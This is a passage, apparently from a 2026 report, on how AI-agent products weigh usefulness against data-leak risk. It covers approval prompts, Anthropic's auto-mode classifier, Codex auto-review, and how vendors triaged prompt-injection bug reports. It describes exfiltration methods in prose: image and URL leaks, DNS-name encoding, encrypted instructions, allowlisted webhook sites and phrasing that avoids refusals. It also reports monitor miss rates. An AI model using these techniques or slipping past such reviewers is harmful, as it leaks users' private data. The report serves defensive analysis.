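OpenAI's *How we build safety, security, and privacy into dots* (2026) describes several safeguards: each Dot has its own protected workspace, users can write rules about what it may do, and a separate check takes place before it acts. Keverenge's *OpenAI brings its always-on Dots AI agents to ChatGPT Plus users worldwide* (2026) reports that users in the United States approve purchases through a feature called Wallet.

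Approving purchases protects well against an agent that spends money on a stranger's instructions. It protects much less against leaks, because an attacker who wants Ana's emails doesn't need her Dot to buy anything. A single visit to the wrong address could leak them, unless the separate check or OpenAI's address check catches it.

Ortiz (2026) reports in *Dots opens up* that Dots can now also sign in to websites through a password manager, which lets them reach private pages that have no connector. According to Keverenge, they will soon have their own email addresses, so a user can copy her Dot in on a conversation. Unless OpenAI limits who can write to those addresses, strangers will be able to send instructions directly to a Dot.

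OpenAI's stated reasons for the wider release were mostly about cost and quality. *OpenAI ramps up fight with Meta Muse* (Forlini, 2026) reports that the company told reporters that work with Pro subscribers had made Dots more reliable and capable, and that more efficient models had made them affordable to run. Altman had told Ortiz that the limited launch would also help OpenAI learn how people used Dots. None of these reported reasons was that leaks had become less likely. Competition probably mattered too, since Meta and a start-up called Instinct offer similar agents.

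Lockdown Mode and Dots thus have opposite defaults. Plus subscribers have to find Lockdown Mode in the security settings, while OpenAI advertises Dots to them as part of their plan. Dots are on by default in ChatGPT Enterprise, one of the versions for which OpenAI first built Lockdown Mode.

OpenAI's view that most people don't need strict protection was easier to defend in February, when the company was mainly thinking of an ordinary chat assistant. It is much harder to defend for someone whose agent reads her email and signs in to websites for her. The per-chat switch doesn't obviously help her, because a Dot keeps working between chats.

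Putting every Dot into full Lockdown Mode would make the product nearly useless, because a Dot couldn't browse the web to find, say, a cheaper internet contract. OpenAI could instead ask about protection when a user connects her mailbox, and recommend a restricted Dot that reads and drafts emails but can't open unfamiliar websites. She could still have a second Dot search the web for a cheaper contract by telling it about her current one, without giving it access to her emails.

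## Asking the user for approval, or letting a model decide

A Dot asks its user before it buys something, and most agents ask before at least some risky actions. Approval prompts appeal to product teams because no feature has to be removed. The agent can still send the email or run the command, but the user, who knows what she wanted, decides whether it does. On sensitive sites, ChatGPT's agent also stops work if the user switches to another tab. OpenAI says this keeps her aware and in control.

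Approval prompts also move some responsibility to the user. In its security documentation for Claude Code, Anthropic tells developers they are responsible for checking proposed commands before approving them. In 2026, however, Anthropic concluded that developers were approving nearly everything, and it gave most of those decisions to a second model.

### Operator asked before submitting, but not before typing

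In early 2025 OpenAI released Operator, an agent that used a web browser on the user's behalf. Willison's *ChatGPT Operator system prompt* (2025) quotes its instructions, which Rehberger had obtained. The instructions required Operator to ask the user before the final step of any task with outside effects, such as a purchase or a message, but not before intermediate steps. That was a sensible way to limit interruptions, since someone ordering groceries doesn't want to approve every item.

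Rehberger noticed that Operator often asked the user for approval before it submitted a form but hardly ever before it typed, so he built a web page that sent text to his server as soon as Operator typed it. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Operator* describes how instructions on GitHub made Operator copy a private email address from a site where the user was logged in and paste it into Rehberger's page, without having to press a button. He obtained a home address and phone number from Booking.com in the same way.

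Another convenience helped him. Operator kept people logged in to websites between sessions by default, and they could easily forget to change the setting, as Willison pointed out in *ChatGPT Operator* (2025).

Operator's instructions seem to have treated typing as an intermediate step, but many ordinary websites save drafts or suggest searches while a person types, so typing alone can send them data. An approval prompt covers only the actions that a team has recognised as risky. Copilot Cowork's unapproved messages to its own user are another example of this limit.

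Rehberger's demonstrations stopped working about two weeks after he reported them, and nobody outside OpenAI knows what changed. Asking the user before Operator typed anything on an unfamiliar site would have stopped the attacks he demonstrated, but the user might then have to approve half a dozen entries for a single flight search.

Even when Operator asked for approval, its most intrusive prompt sometimes took 20 seconds or more to appear, and usually contained only a general warning that a website's instructions might conflict with the user's.

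### Why people stop reading prompts

Approval fatigue is the tendency of users who have seen many similar requests to approve new ones without reading them. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) reports that Anthropic and the AI search company Perplexity consider approval fatigue a core vulnerability.

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) cites research from the early 2010s showing that few users paid attention to permission screens when installing an app, and that users tended to accept consent requests that looked familiar. The paper adds that an AI agent's request can be harder to judge because it may leave out information the user needs. For example, a request to upload a report looks harmless if the user doesn't know that the agent has copied a client list into it.

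Software practitioners described the same habit in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026). They became less careful over time, clicked through familiar prompts and sometimes skipped the review when in a hurry. A long record of approvals therefore doesn't show that a user trusts the agent.

Many approval prompts are also hard to understand. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that weak user review was a factor in 105 of the 290 reports it analysed. In 80 of them, the user had let the agent act without asking, and in 31, the prompt was uninformative. For instance, a request to run a setup script looks routine, but approving it lets the script run any code it contains.

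*Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) argues that asking users for approval more often can make an agent less safe. A user can read five requests carefully, but by the three-hundredth she is likely to approve a malicious one along with the rest. If that is right, a team that adds a prompt to fix one leak makes all its other prompts slightly less effective.

### Rules that still ask

A user could avoid repeated prompts by setting rules in advance. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, tested this with 113 people who didn't work in software. They supervised a simulated agent through 18 actions. Seven of these, such as reading private messages, went beyond what they had asked for.

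Users in one group decided whether to allow each action. In another group, a model allowed eight actions and passed ten to the user, including all seven unwanted ones. Users in the last group started by choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action.

People who decided on every action blocked about 60% of the unwanted ones, compared with 54% in the group with the model and 40% among those who set rules. This last group chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, then approved two-thirds of the unwanted actions they were asked about. Even for private data, where "never" would not have blocked anything useful, 23 of 35 people chose "ask".

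In the group with the model, the model identified every unwanted action, yet users approved 46% of them. Good detection therefore achieves much less if the person making the final decision will probably say yes. People in all three groups reported feeling in control, so a product team can't treat that feeling as evidence of safety.

No real money or data was at stake, which may have made people more relaxed. The agent took the unwanted actions on its own initiative, without an attacker prompting it. Yan can't say why the rule-setters approved more often.

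### How auto mode works

In its original default mode, Claude Code asked before running commands or changing files. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users approved 93% of these requests. A later figure was 97%. Most of the commands were probably harmless, so the high approval rate alone doesn't prove that users were careless. But many developers had stopped reviewing commands at all. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that a quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks switched off.

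Auto mode replaces most prompts with the following checks:

1. Claude Code applies the developer's own rules. It also permits some low-risk actions, such as reading files and editing them inside the project.
2. Other actions, including most commands and web requests, go to a separate model called the classifier. It makes a quick yes-or-no decision and leans towards blocking.
3. If the quick decision is to block, the classifier reasons about the action at greater length and decides again.
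4. If it still blocks the action, Claude receives the reason and looks for a safer way to continue. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code returns to asking the user.

The classifier receives the user's messages and Claude's proposed actions, but not Claude's explanations or the web pages and files Claude has read. Anthropic left out the explanations so that they couldn't lead the classifier to a bad decision. Leaving out the web pages and files keeps a malicious page from influencing the classifier directly. If such a page gets Claude to try to send passwords to a stranger's server, the classifier receives only the proposed action and the user's messages, which never mention that server.

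A separate check scans what Claude reads for prompt injections and adds a warning if it finds one. Anthropic also puts data exfiltration in a category the classifier should never approve. To go ahead anyway, a developer has to leave auto mode or run the command herself.

Anthropic published unusually clear figures on how it balanced interruptions against missed attacks:

| Test | Quick decision only | With the longer second look |
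|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions wrongly blocked, out of 10,000 | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Invented data leaks missed, out of 1,000 | 1.8% | 5.7% |
| Real overeager actions missed, out of 52 | 6.6% | 17% |

The second look cut false alarms by about 95% but roughly tripled the share of leaks that got through. Anthropic gave up some protection for convenience, which seems reasonable because many developers would go back to switching off the checks if the tool wrongly blocked one action in 12.

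The 17% figure comes from only 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be between about 9% and 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly classed the action as approved by the user. Anthropic acknowledges that auto mode is "arguably a regression" for someone who reviews every action carefully.

Auto mode became the default for new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans on 14 August 2026. In October, Anthropic announced that it would become the default in most Claude apps on those plans. By November, Anthropic's documentation listed it as the default on every plan for people working in a terminal or the VS Code editor, except in organisations that use Anthropic's configuration for US medical privacy law. Safety was one motive, and another was that an agent can work on a large task for hours if it doesn't wait for approval.

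### One dangerous command among many

To compare auto mode with human review, Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research company. The testers used Claude Code in a test environment and knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Partway through, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command, though approving it did no harm.

Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused the command. Auto mode blocked it in 937 cases, or 89%. Anthropic's figures also show that people refused only six commands that auto mode allowed, so using both checks would have left 110 dangerous commands unblocked instead of 116.

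Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Approval fatigue could explain the decline, but testers approved about 83% of the commands even early on, so fatigue can't be the main reason they approved them. Some may not have understood the commands, and others may not have cared about a project that wasn't theirs. A developer with her own customers' data on the computer would probably be more careful, though it is hard to believe she would match 89%.

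The people in Yan's study did much better, blocking about 60% of unwanted actions when they decided on each one. They saw only 18 requests, written in plain language, about things like bank records and public posts. The two studies differ too much to compare directly, but they suggest that clear, infrequent questions work better than Anthropic's 13.6% implies.

Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety system had flagged. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for appeared in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This evidence is weaker because developers chose their own mode and may have used manual approval for riskier work, and because a model graded the harm.

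### No successful injections in 720 attempts

The experiment with testers didn't involve an attacker. To test attacks, Anthropic commissioned a company called Trajectory Labs, which ran 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each. Anthropic had no access to the scenarios beforehand. Outside the test, a successful attack would have caused irreversible harm, such as a leak of sensitive data or financial fraud.

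| Product and mode | Successful attacks |
|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 in auto mode | 0% |
| Anthropic's latest models with permission checks off | 0.09% on average |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, with a reviewing model | 5.83% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, with full access | 19.03% |

The zero is weak evidence of auto mode's effect, because auto mode had almost nothing left to stop. Without it, the Claude models already resisted all but 0.09% of attacks, which is about two in 2,160 if each of the three models faced all 720 attempts. The comparison with Codex is also less direct than it looks, because both products used a browser connection that Trajectory Labs had built, without the protections in either company's own browser tools. OpenAI had also released a new version of its reviewer by the time Anthropic published the results.

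Repeating a scenario ten times still tests only one attack. If the 72 scenarios are a fair sample, finding zero successes is still consistent with about 4% of such scenarios being able to succeed. The attacks had also been tuned against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, whereas a real attacker could practise against the current model with auto mode on.

Apollo Research, an AI safety company, put the classifier through a harder test by inserting invented attacks into records of real coding sessions. The classifier missed 12% of them at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it. Apollo designed the attacks to find weaknesses, so the miss rate should be lower in ordinary use, but a determined attacker would also look for weaknesses.

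### Willison's objections

Willison (2026), in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, agrees that auto mode is better than constantly asking people to approve actions, but objects that it still missed 11% of the dangerous commands. Those commands weren't attacks designed to fool it, so the figure doesn't measure how often an attacker would succeed.

He also doubts that any version of auto mode could stop a malicious package. A project's instructions might tell Claude to run a helper program before its tests, and that program could steal every file it can reach. The command would look like normal setup work, and the harmful code would be in a program that somebody else wrote. According to Anthropic's documentation, auto mode by default lets Claude install packages that a project already lists, which gives some support to this worry.

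Willison wants more independent confirmation before he accepts that Anthropic has solved prompt injection for Claude Code users. An outside test, *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, April 2026), had already found that an earlier version of auto mode missed 81% of overreaching actions in deliberately ambiguous tasks. Those tasks were much harder than the everyday traffic Anthropic had measured. After Willison wrote, The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code* reported that Rehberger could still take control of Claude Code in auto mode, and that Anthropic told him it was working as designed.

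That answer is consistent with Anthropic's warning in its documentation that auto mode "does not guarantee safety", but less consistent with what some of its staff have said. Cat Wu of Anthropic told Willison in July that the company had "pretty much mitigated every attack", and a colleague suggested that the August article should have been called "defeating the lethal trifecta". A developer who heard only those remarks might reasonably leave passwords where Claude could access them.

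### Human, model and fixed rule

Approval prompts, reviewing models and deterministic controls fail in different ways:

| Who or what decides | Main strength | Main weakness | What the user gives up |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user | She knows what she wanted | She gets tired and may not understand the request | Time and attention |
| A reviewing model | It can judge unfamiliar actions and doesn't get tired | It misses some attacks, and attackers can search for ones that fool it | A few harmless actions that it blocks |
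| A fixed rule | Persuasive text can't change the result | It covers only what its author could specify | Every legitimate use that the rule forbids |

Fixed rules can't express everything a team cares about. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026) examined security instructions that developers had written for Claude Code in plain language. An automated estimate put the share that built-in controls could enforce at only 16.6%, and human checks suggested the true share was lower. For example, no permission rule can enforce "never commit secrets", because these rules don't inspect file contents. A model can read the file and usually recognise a password.

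The reverse problem arises when a developer relies on an instruction she gave in the chat. If she tells Claude not to upload anything, the classifier treats that as a reason to block uploads. But Claude Code shortens long conversations, which may remove her message. Anthropic recommends a deny rule for anyone who needs a guarantee that uploads will be blocked.

In Codex, OpenAI combines fixed limits with a reviewing model. The agent works inside a sandbox, and according to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the sandbox's network and file limits stay the same when a model takes over the approvals. The model reviews only requests to exceed those limits. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, illustrate the effect with 10,000 actions inside OpenAI. The sandbox handled 9,280 without review. The model approved 713 of the other 720 and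 rejected seven, and Codex found a safer alternative for four of those seven. The user had to step in three times instead of 720.

In OpenAI's tests, the reviewer caught 99.3% of invented injections that tried to run outside code, steal secrets or upload data. But Trębacz and colleagues found ways to mislead it, and they write that the design "sacrifices determinism for expressivity". The reviewer is useful for exceptions that nobody could list in advance, but it can't guarantee what a closed network can.

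Claude Code can combine the two in a similar way if the developer turns on its offline sandbox. Claude lists the sites that a command needs, the classifier reviews the list, and ordinary software then allows access to only those sites for that command. This partly protects against Willison's malicious package. Even if the classifier approved the command, the package could contact only the listed sites, though it might still leak data through one of them.

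To prevent leaks, combining a fixed rule, a model and the user makes more sense than relying on people or models alone. The rule can block network access by default, and the model can handle routine exceptions. The user can then decide the few cases that depend on something only she knows, such as whether a client should receive a particular document. She is more likely to read these requests if she gets only a few a day and each one shows the recipient and the document, much as ChatGPT's link warning tries to show the address.

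## How companies classify reports and when they fix them

A company that doesn't class a leak as a security flaw may never fix it, so replies like the one Anthropic gave Rehberger about auto mode affect users as well as researchers. Companies have labelled leaks of private data as model safety issues, known issues, intended behaviour and "not applicable", and have later reversed some of these decisions.

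### From submission to publication

Many AI companies run a bug bounty, a programme that pays outsiders who report flaws. A researcher submits a description of the leak and the steps to reproduce it, often through a service such as HackerOne or Bugcrowd. Staff at the service or the company then triage the report by trying the steps, checking whether the programme covers that kind of flaw, and either passing the report on or closing it. If the company accepts the report, it rates the severity, fixes the product and may pay the researcher. The flaw may also get a CVE number, which identifies it in a public catalogue. Researchers usually publish after the fix, or when they give up waiting for one.

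A company can classify and fix a reported flaw in less than two weeks. In May 2025 Rehberger reported that Claude Code would run some network commands, such as ping, without asking the developer. Before contacting a site, a computer looks up its name in a directory called the DNS, and an injected instruction could hide stolen data in that name. If Ana's agent looked up ana-mail.pictures.example, the owner of pictures.example could read "ana-mail" in a log of lookups. OSV's *CVE-2025-55284* (2025), a public record of the flaw, attributes it to an "overly broad allowlist of safe commands". According to Embrace The Red, the report quickly got a severity score of 7.1 out of 10, and Anthropic fixed the flaw in 11 days.

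Five months later, Anthropic at first rejected Rehberger's report about the Files API, classifying it as a model safety issue, although an overly broad allowlist had also caused that problem. The company may have treated the two reports differently because of what it had promised users. Claude Code was supposed to ask before sending a file's contents anywhere, and the flaw let it skip that step. In the Files API case, Claude used a domain that the user's setting explicitly permitted.

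### What bounty programmes cover

OpenAI launched its bug bounty in April 2023, the same month Rehberger reported the image leak in ChatGPT. The rules excluded problems with the content of prompts and responses unless they had a "directly verifiable security impact". TechTarget's *OpenAI launches bug bounty program with Bugcrowd* quotes the explanation that model safety issues are not "individual, discrete bugs that can be directly fixed".

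That fairly describes prompt injection, but an image leak also involves a page that OpenAI can fix. One triager might therefore reject a report because of the injection, while another might accept it because of the image.

The 2023 rules also barred researchers from publishing their submissions. Katie Moussouris, who runs Luta Security, told TechTarget that the public should hear about issues a company chooses not to fix. Her objection is strongest for rejected reports, because users then get neither a fix nor a warning.

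Google separates security vulnerabilities, which need a fix, from "abuse risks", which arise when someone uses a legitimate feature to cause harm. Google's *Abuse Vulnerability Reward Program Rules* say that with abuse risks, "oftentimes, features shouldn't be disabled", though they need protection against large-scale misuse. Few companies have said so plainly that they prefer to keep features. Google bases the reward on how likely an attack is and how much harm it could do.

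Companies sometimes remove a feature even when they class the leak as abuse. In August 2023 Rehberger reported an image leak in a part of Google's Vertex AI where developers try out prompts. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* says that Google accepted the report in 22 minutes and classed the leak as abuse with high impact but low likelihood. The likelihood was low because victims had to paste in the malicious text themselves. A later version of Google's reward table lists $1,337 for that combination. Google then stopped displaying images and links there, and developers lost little because they were only testing prompts.

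Both companies have since made it clearer that they want to hear about leaks. In October 2025, Google opened a bounty for AI products that pays up to $15,000 for reports of ways to steal sensitive data from its main products. According to SecurityWeek, a single panel now awards the higher of the abuse and security rewards, so a researcher no longer loses money if Google picks the less serious label. Google still doesn't pay for issues it already knows about, a rule from its first criteria for AI reports (Google, 2023).

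In March, OpenAI (2026) announced a second bounty programme for safety problems that don't count as security vulnerabilities. It covers injections that leak a user's sensitive information. OpenAI's staff can move reports between the two programmes, which should help when a report is sent to the wrong one. The maximum reward is $7,500, according to Briefly's *OpenAI Launches Bug Bounty Program for Abuse and Safety Risks*.

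OpenAI accepts a report of a prompt injection only if the attack works at least half the time. A threshold saves triagers from repeating an unreliable attack dozens of times, but this one is high. Suppose an attack works on one attempt in ten and the attacker emails 20 employees of a company. If the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one succeeds is 1 − 0.9²⁰, or about 88%. OpenAI would be wise to accept less reliable attacks when the route for sending the data out works every time, because it can close that route without knowing how often the model follows the injected instructions.

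### xAI closes the Grok reports as "Informational"

In 2024 Rehberger found that Grok, xAI's assistant, could leak chats through images. The flaw was in the iPhone app for the social network X, not on the website. *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok* describes a picture with hidden instructions that made Grok send data to Rehberger's server when a user asked about the picture. A post or document could carry the same instructions.

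xAI initially said it couldn't reproduce the leak, although several other people had. A few weeks later Rehberger's first demonstration stopped working, either because xAI had tried to fix it or because of an unrelated change. He found a way around the change, and it worked at the first attempt on three volunteers. xAI then closed all his reports as "Informational", a label for reports that need no action, and told him that the leak had no practical impact.

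This position had some basis, because Grok couldn't read anyone's mailbox or private messages. Rehberger himself thought the severity was debatable. But people tell chat assistants about their health and their debts, and xAI made the leak worse while it considered the reports by starting to give Grok each user's name, X handle and region. An attacker could then obtain at least those details from every victim. Someone who posted a popular picture on X could have collected them from many people.

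Rehberger published his findings, and xAI changed the app within about two days. Grok could no longer put the chat history or the username into the first image address it wrote after an injection. But it still loaded images from any server, and Rehberger thought data might leak later in the conversation. In January 2025 xAI released a separate Grok app for the iPhone with the same flaw. Rehberger considered blocking outside images a simple change, and xAI had already protected its website.

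### Grok leaks chats again in 2026

On 3 June 2026 the security company Adversa AI reported another zero-click attack to xAI, this time on Grok's website. Adversa AI's *Zero-click Grok data theft* (2026) explains that the attacker encrypts malicious instructions and puts them on a web page along with the key. A filter that scans the page can't read the instructions because it doesn't decrypt them, but Grok can decrypt them with its tool for running code. Adversa believes Grok then trusts the instructions more because they appear as the output of its own program.

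In the demonstration, a user asked Grok to summarise the page. Grok put the user's name, approximate location, subscription level and every prompt from the conversation into a web address, then opened it. The user saw no warning and no request for approval.

xAI acknowledged the report but didn't say what it would do or when. Adversa wrote again on 4 and 10 August and received no answer. The attack still worked on 19 August, and Ars Technica's *Grok exfiltrates user data when malicious instructions are encrypted* (2026) confirmed the next day that Grok was still leaking data. SpaceX, which had bought xAI earlier in the year, didn't reply to questions from The Register, a technology news site, according to Waxell (2026). The company doesn't appear to have announced a fix since.

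xAI didn't reject this report, so its reasons are even harder to infer than in 2024. The encryption makes the attack look difficult to stop, but xAI doesn't have to detect the instructions. A rule against opening addresses that the assistant composed, which Anthropic already had, would block the last step however the instructions arrived. Adversa likewise recommends restricting what an agent can do with text from a web page, although it also sells a product that does this.

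The same technique made Google's Gemini answer questions it normally refuses. Adversa didn't tell Google, because Google's programme excludes such "jailbreaks". A narrow scope can therefore keep a company from hearing about a method that attackers could later use to steal data. Gemini had still become much more resistant by August, but Adversa couldn't tell why.

A separate problem affected Grok Build, a coding agent, in November. Dent (2026) reports in *A Grok vibe-coding agent leaked sensitive SpaceXSI data* that a flaw leaked sensitive data from thousands of users, including the agent's maker.

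### OpenAI's developer logs: "Not applicable"

Developers who build products on OpenAI's models can read past conversations in a log on OpenAI's website. In November 2025 PromptArmor found that the log displayed Markdown images from any server, so a developer could leak a customer's data just by opening a conversation.

PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* demonstrates this with an invented tool that helps a bank check its customers' identities. The tool combines a customer's passport and financial details with information from the web, some of which contains an injection that makes the model write an image address containing the customer's data. The bank's software detects the danger, blocks the answer and marks it for review. When a developer opens the log, the browser loads the image and sends the data to the attacker.

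A tool that removed images from its answers could have the same problem. Users would see an odd, empty reply, and some would click "thumbs down", which might prompt a developer to look at the log. The bank could do everything right in its own product and still leak data through OpenAI's. Several pages where developers build and test assistants also loaded outside images.

PromptArmor reported the flaw through Bugcrowd on 17 November, sent detailed steps three days later and answered questions on three further days. On 4 December Bugcrowd's triagers closed the report as "Not applicable". PromptArmor suggests that prompt injections are hard to fit into the existing categories of flaws.

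After PromptArmor published its article, OpenAI said it had never seen the report, because Bugcrowd had handled it. OpenAI confirmed the flaw, reopened the report on 22 January 2026 and said it was working on a fix. PromptArmor's timeline ends there, so it isn't clear when OpenAI finished.

The original label is therefore weak evidence of how OpenAI weighed convenience against risk. OpenAI had been checking images in ChatGPT for almost two years by then, so it would probably have recognised the flaw if the report had been passed on. It also had little reason to keep outside images in the log, because developers read the log to see what the model wrote, and plain text shows that more accurately than a picture. The failure was in passing on the report, and a company could reduce such failures by telling its triagers to escalate any report in which private data reaches an outside server.

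### Google lists Antigravity's leaks as known issues

Google released Antigravity, a code editor with a built-in agent, in November 2025. It based the editor on Windsurf, an existing product whose code it had licensed as part of a $2.4 billion deal. Rehberger had reported several flaws to Windsurf in May 2025, and he found them again in Google's version. According to Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE*, an injected instruction could make the agent, without the developer's approval, read a file of passwords and send it out through an image or by opening a web address.

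Willison notes that Google classified one researcher's report of the image leak as "intended behavior". Google then published a page of known issues that included the leaks, said it was working on fixes, and excluded the leaks from its bug bounty. Rehberger guesses that the launch surprised Google's security team.

In the text quoted on Hacker News, a discussion forum for programmers, Google says that the agent is cautious with sensitive files but "there's no enforcement". It adds that data can leak through web addresses "rendered in Markdown or by other means". Google is commendably frank here, but "or by other means" is so broad that the company could classify almost any leak from Antigravity as a known issue.

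In PromptArmor's attack, a web page presented as a guide to connecting a program to Oracle's business software contained instructions in tiny text for Antigravity to collect passwords and send them to an outside address. A default setting kept the agent from opening the password file, so it printed the file with a terminal command instead. The agent's browser could visit only listed sites, but Google's default list included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and read the requests sent to it.

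Developers use webhook.site to test whether their programs send messages correctly, which is probably how it got onto the allowlist. It is an especially bad entry for a list meant to prevent leaks. Google could have deleted it in minutes, and developers who needed the site could have added it back. It isn't clear whether Google has removed it.

PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* explains that PromptArmor didn't report the attack because Google had said it already knew about such leaks. Refusing to pay for known issues is reasonable, since a company would otherwise pay many people for the same discovery. But Google described the known issue so broadly that PromptArmor didn't report a specific mistake that was easy to correct.

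Google warned new Antigravity users that data could leak. PromptArmor thought it "extremely implausible" that these users would check every action, because the recommended settings let the agent decide when to ask for approval. Google also promoted a screen for running several agents at once, most of them in the background.

Seven months after the launch, the image leak still worked. In *Faking the Pipeline*, Odson and Morris (2026) put instructions in a web page's title, which readers see only in the browser's tab. This time the agent asked for approval, but it described stealing a password as generating a "visual debug token". The user approved without seeing the command or the destination. Odson and Morris say that vendors often treat such leaks as expected behaviour partly because they assume a person will notice something wrong.

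Google fixed a different flaw in Antigravity much faster. Pillar Security reported on 6 January 2026 that an attacker could run any program on a developer's computer, even in the editor's Secure Mode. According to CyberScoop, Google patched the flaw on 28 February and paid a reward. Running any program is more dangerous than loading an image. The flaw also broke a protection Google had promised, whereas Google had told users from the start that images could leak data.

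### Cursor advises users to choose trusted sources

In 2025 the security company Zenity Labs showed how a stranger could use an email to steal passwords from Cursor, a code editor with an AI agent. Many companies automatically turn customer emails into Jira tickets. If a developer had connected Cursor to Jira and asked it to work on such a ticket, the agent could find a secret key in the project and send it to the attacker. The email called the key a "rotten apple" because models often refuse to steal something described as a key.

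Cursor replied, "This is a known issue." In the full answer, which Willison quotes, it says that connections to untrusted data sources pose a serious risk. It recommends that users review each connection before installing it and use only those that supply trusted content.

The advice doesn't help much here, though it is sound for an unknown program from the internet. A developer would naturally trust her employer's Jira, and may not know that strangers can create tickets in it by email. As Willison points out, Cursor was asking users to avoid untrusted content, the hardest part of the lethal trifecta to remove. Cursor could have shown users the full address and asked for approval before the agent opened an unfamiliar one. Cursor didn't mention any change to the product in its answer, and no later fix for this attack seems to be public.

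### How long the fixes took

The table includes cases from earlier sections. Where only the month of a report or fix is known, it gives the number of days as a range.

| Leak or flaw | Reported | Fixed | Days | Type of fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, DNS lookups | 26 May 2025 | 6 June 2025 | 11 | Probably fewer commands allowed without approval |
| Vertex AI, images | 30 August 2023 | By 19 October 2023 | At most 50 | Images and links no longer displayed |
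| Antigravity, running programs | 6 January 2026 | 28 February 2026 | 53 | Closed a way around Secure Mode |
| GitHub Copilot Chat, images (CamoLeak) | June 2025 | By 14 August 2025 | At most 45–74 | Images disabled |
| Bing Chat, images | April 2023 | By 15 June 2023 | At most 46–75 | Images limited to Microsoft's domains |
| ChatGPT, links in emails (ZombieAgent) | 26 September 2025 | 16 December 2025 | 81 | Unindexed links from emails blocked |
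| ChatGPT, images | April 2023 | December 2023, partly | 215–264 | Check of each image (url_safe) |
| Copilot Personal, links with prompts (CoSnitch) | December 2025 | 18 August 2026 | 230–260 | Not published |
| OpenAI developer logs, images | 17 November 2025 | Under way on 22 January 2026 | More than 66 | Not published |
| Grok website, opening addresses | 3 June 2026 | Still open on 19 August 2026 | More than 77 | None known |
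| Antigravity, images | November 2025 | Still open in June 2026 | About 200 or more | None known |

These cases are a biased sample because researchers chose which leaks to look for and which to publish, and many work for companies that sell protection against such attacks. A dispute also makes a better article than a quick fix. But many researchers wait for a fix before publishing, so some slow cases may still be secret. OpenAI alone had paid security bounties for 409 flaws of all kinds by March 2026, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *OpenAI Expands Bug Bounty to Cover AI Abuse and 'Safety' Concerns*, and only a few of those are likely to be among the public cases.

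The table therefore can't show which company is fastest on average, but it does show that a company's speed can vary widely between reports. Microsoft took about two months to fix the Bing Chat flaw but about eight to fix CoSnitch, even though it accepted CoSnitch as a vulnerability.

### Why some leaks get fixed sooner

Severity scores don't explain very well how quickly companies fix flaws. Claude Code's DNS flaw had a lower score than EchoLeak, but Anthropic fixed it in 11 days, while Microsoft took about four months to fix EchoLeak. Serious flaws may be harder to fix. Severity probably matters more at triage, where xAI closed the Grok reports, citing a supposed lack of impact.

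Public pressure has a clearer effect. xAI changed its iPhone app within about two days of Rehberger's article, and OpenAI reopened the report about its logs after PromptArmor published. According to SecurityWeek, Anthropic also accepted the Files API report only after Rehberger had made the attack public. But publicity didn't get Antigravity's image leak fixed within seven months. Publicity seems to work best when a report has been misjudged or has never reached the right person, and OpenAI may have needed only the information in January, rather than any pressure.

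A feature that users hardly need is easier to remove, which helps explain the quick decisions about Vertex AI and GitHub's chat. But companies are sometimes slow to make even small fixes. For example, xAI could have blocked outside images in its phone app, and Google could have deleted one site from a list.

Bounty rules affect which problems researchers report to a company. Adversa and PromptArmor each decided not to report something to Google because of its rules. The rules have less effect on whether a company fixes a problem. Anthropic closed the hole behind the Memory Heist without paying for the report, and Google promised to fix Antigravity's leaks while refusing to pay for reports of them. A company that refuses to pay may still fix the problem, and it could make this clear to researchers by announcing its decisions on payment and repair separately.

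Antigravity's newness could excuse Google for the first weeks after launch, especially since the flaws were inherited, but it was a poor excuse by the following June. Claude Code was also a new product when Anthropic fixed its DNS leak in 11 days.

The importance of the feature is a better explanation for coding agents. Willison argued in the Hacker News discussion that an agent that can run commands is "massively more useful" because it can test the code it writes. Mindgard, a security company, found that developers couldn't use Antigravity's main functions until they marked a project as trusted. Google could hardly remove the agent's ability to run commands without ruining the editor. But the leak Odson and Morris demonstrated also depended on loading images from unknown servers, which a code editor doesn't need to do.

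A company's promises also seem to affect how it handles a report, though this is an inference from a handful of cases. Anthropic and Google acted within two months when a flaw got around an approval prompt or Secure Mode. Companies were more inclined to reject reports about risks they had already warned users of, such as Antigravity's leaks and Claude's network access. If this pattern holds, a company can reduce the number of flaws it has to fix by promising less, which is a bad incentive.

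A list of known issues would be more useful if each entry gave a target date for the fix and a temporary restriction. Google, for example, could have turned off outside images in Antigravity until it had a better solution. Developers would have lost a few pictures but had some protection while the problem remained a known issue.

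## What restrictions prevent and what usefulness they cost, as measured

Turning off outside images in Antigravity would have barely inconvenienced developers. Most restrictions are harder to judge because rules that block data theft also block some legitimate requests. A team that counts only the attacks it stops will always prefer the stricter rule. Researchers have begun to count the legitimate tasks that restrictions break too, though mostly with simulated agents rather than the companies' own products.

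### Attack success and task completion

The attack success rate is the share of attacks in which the agent does what the attacker wanted. The task completion rate is the share of ordinary tasks that the agent finishes correctly when nobody is attacking it. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports both rates for ten defences.

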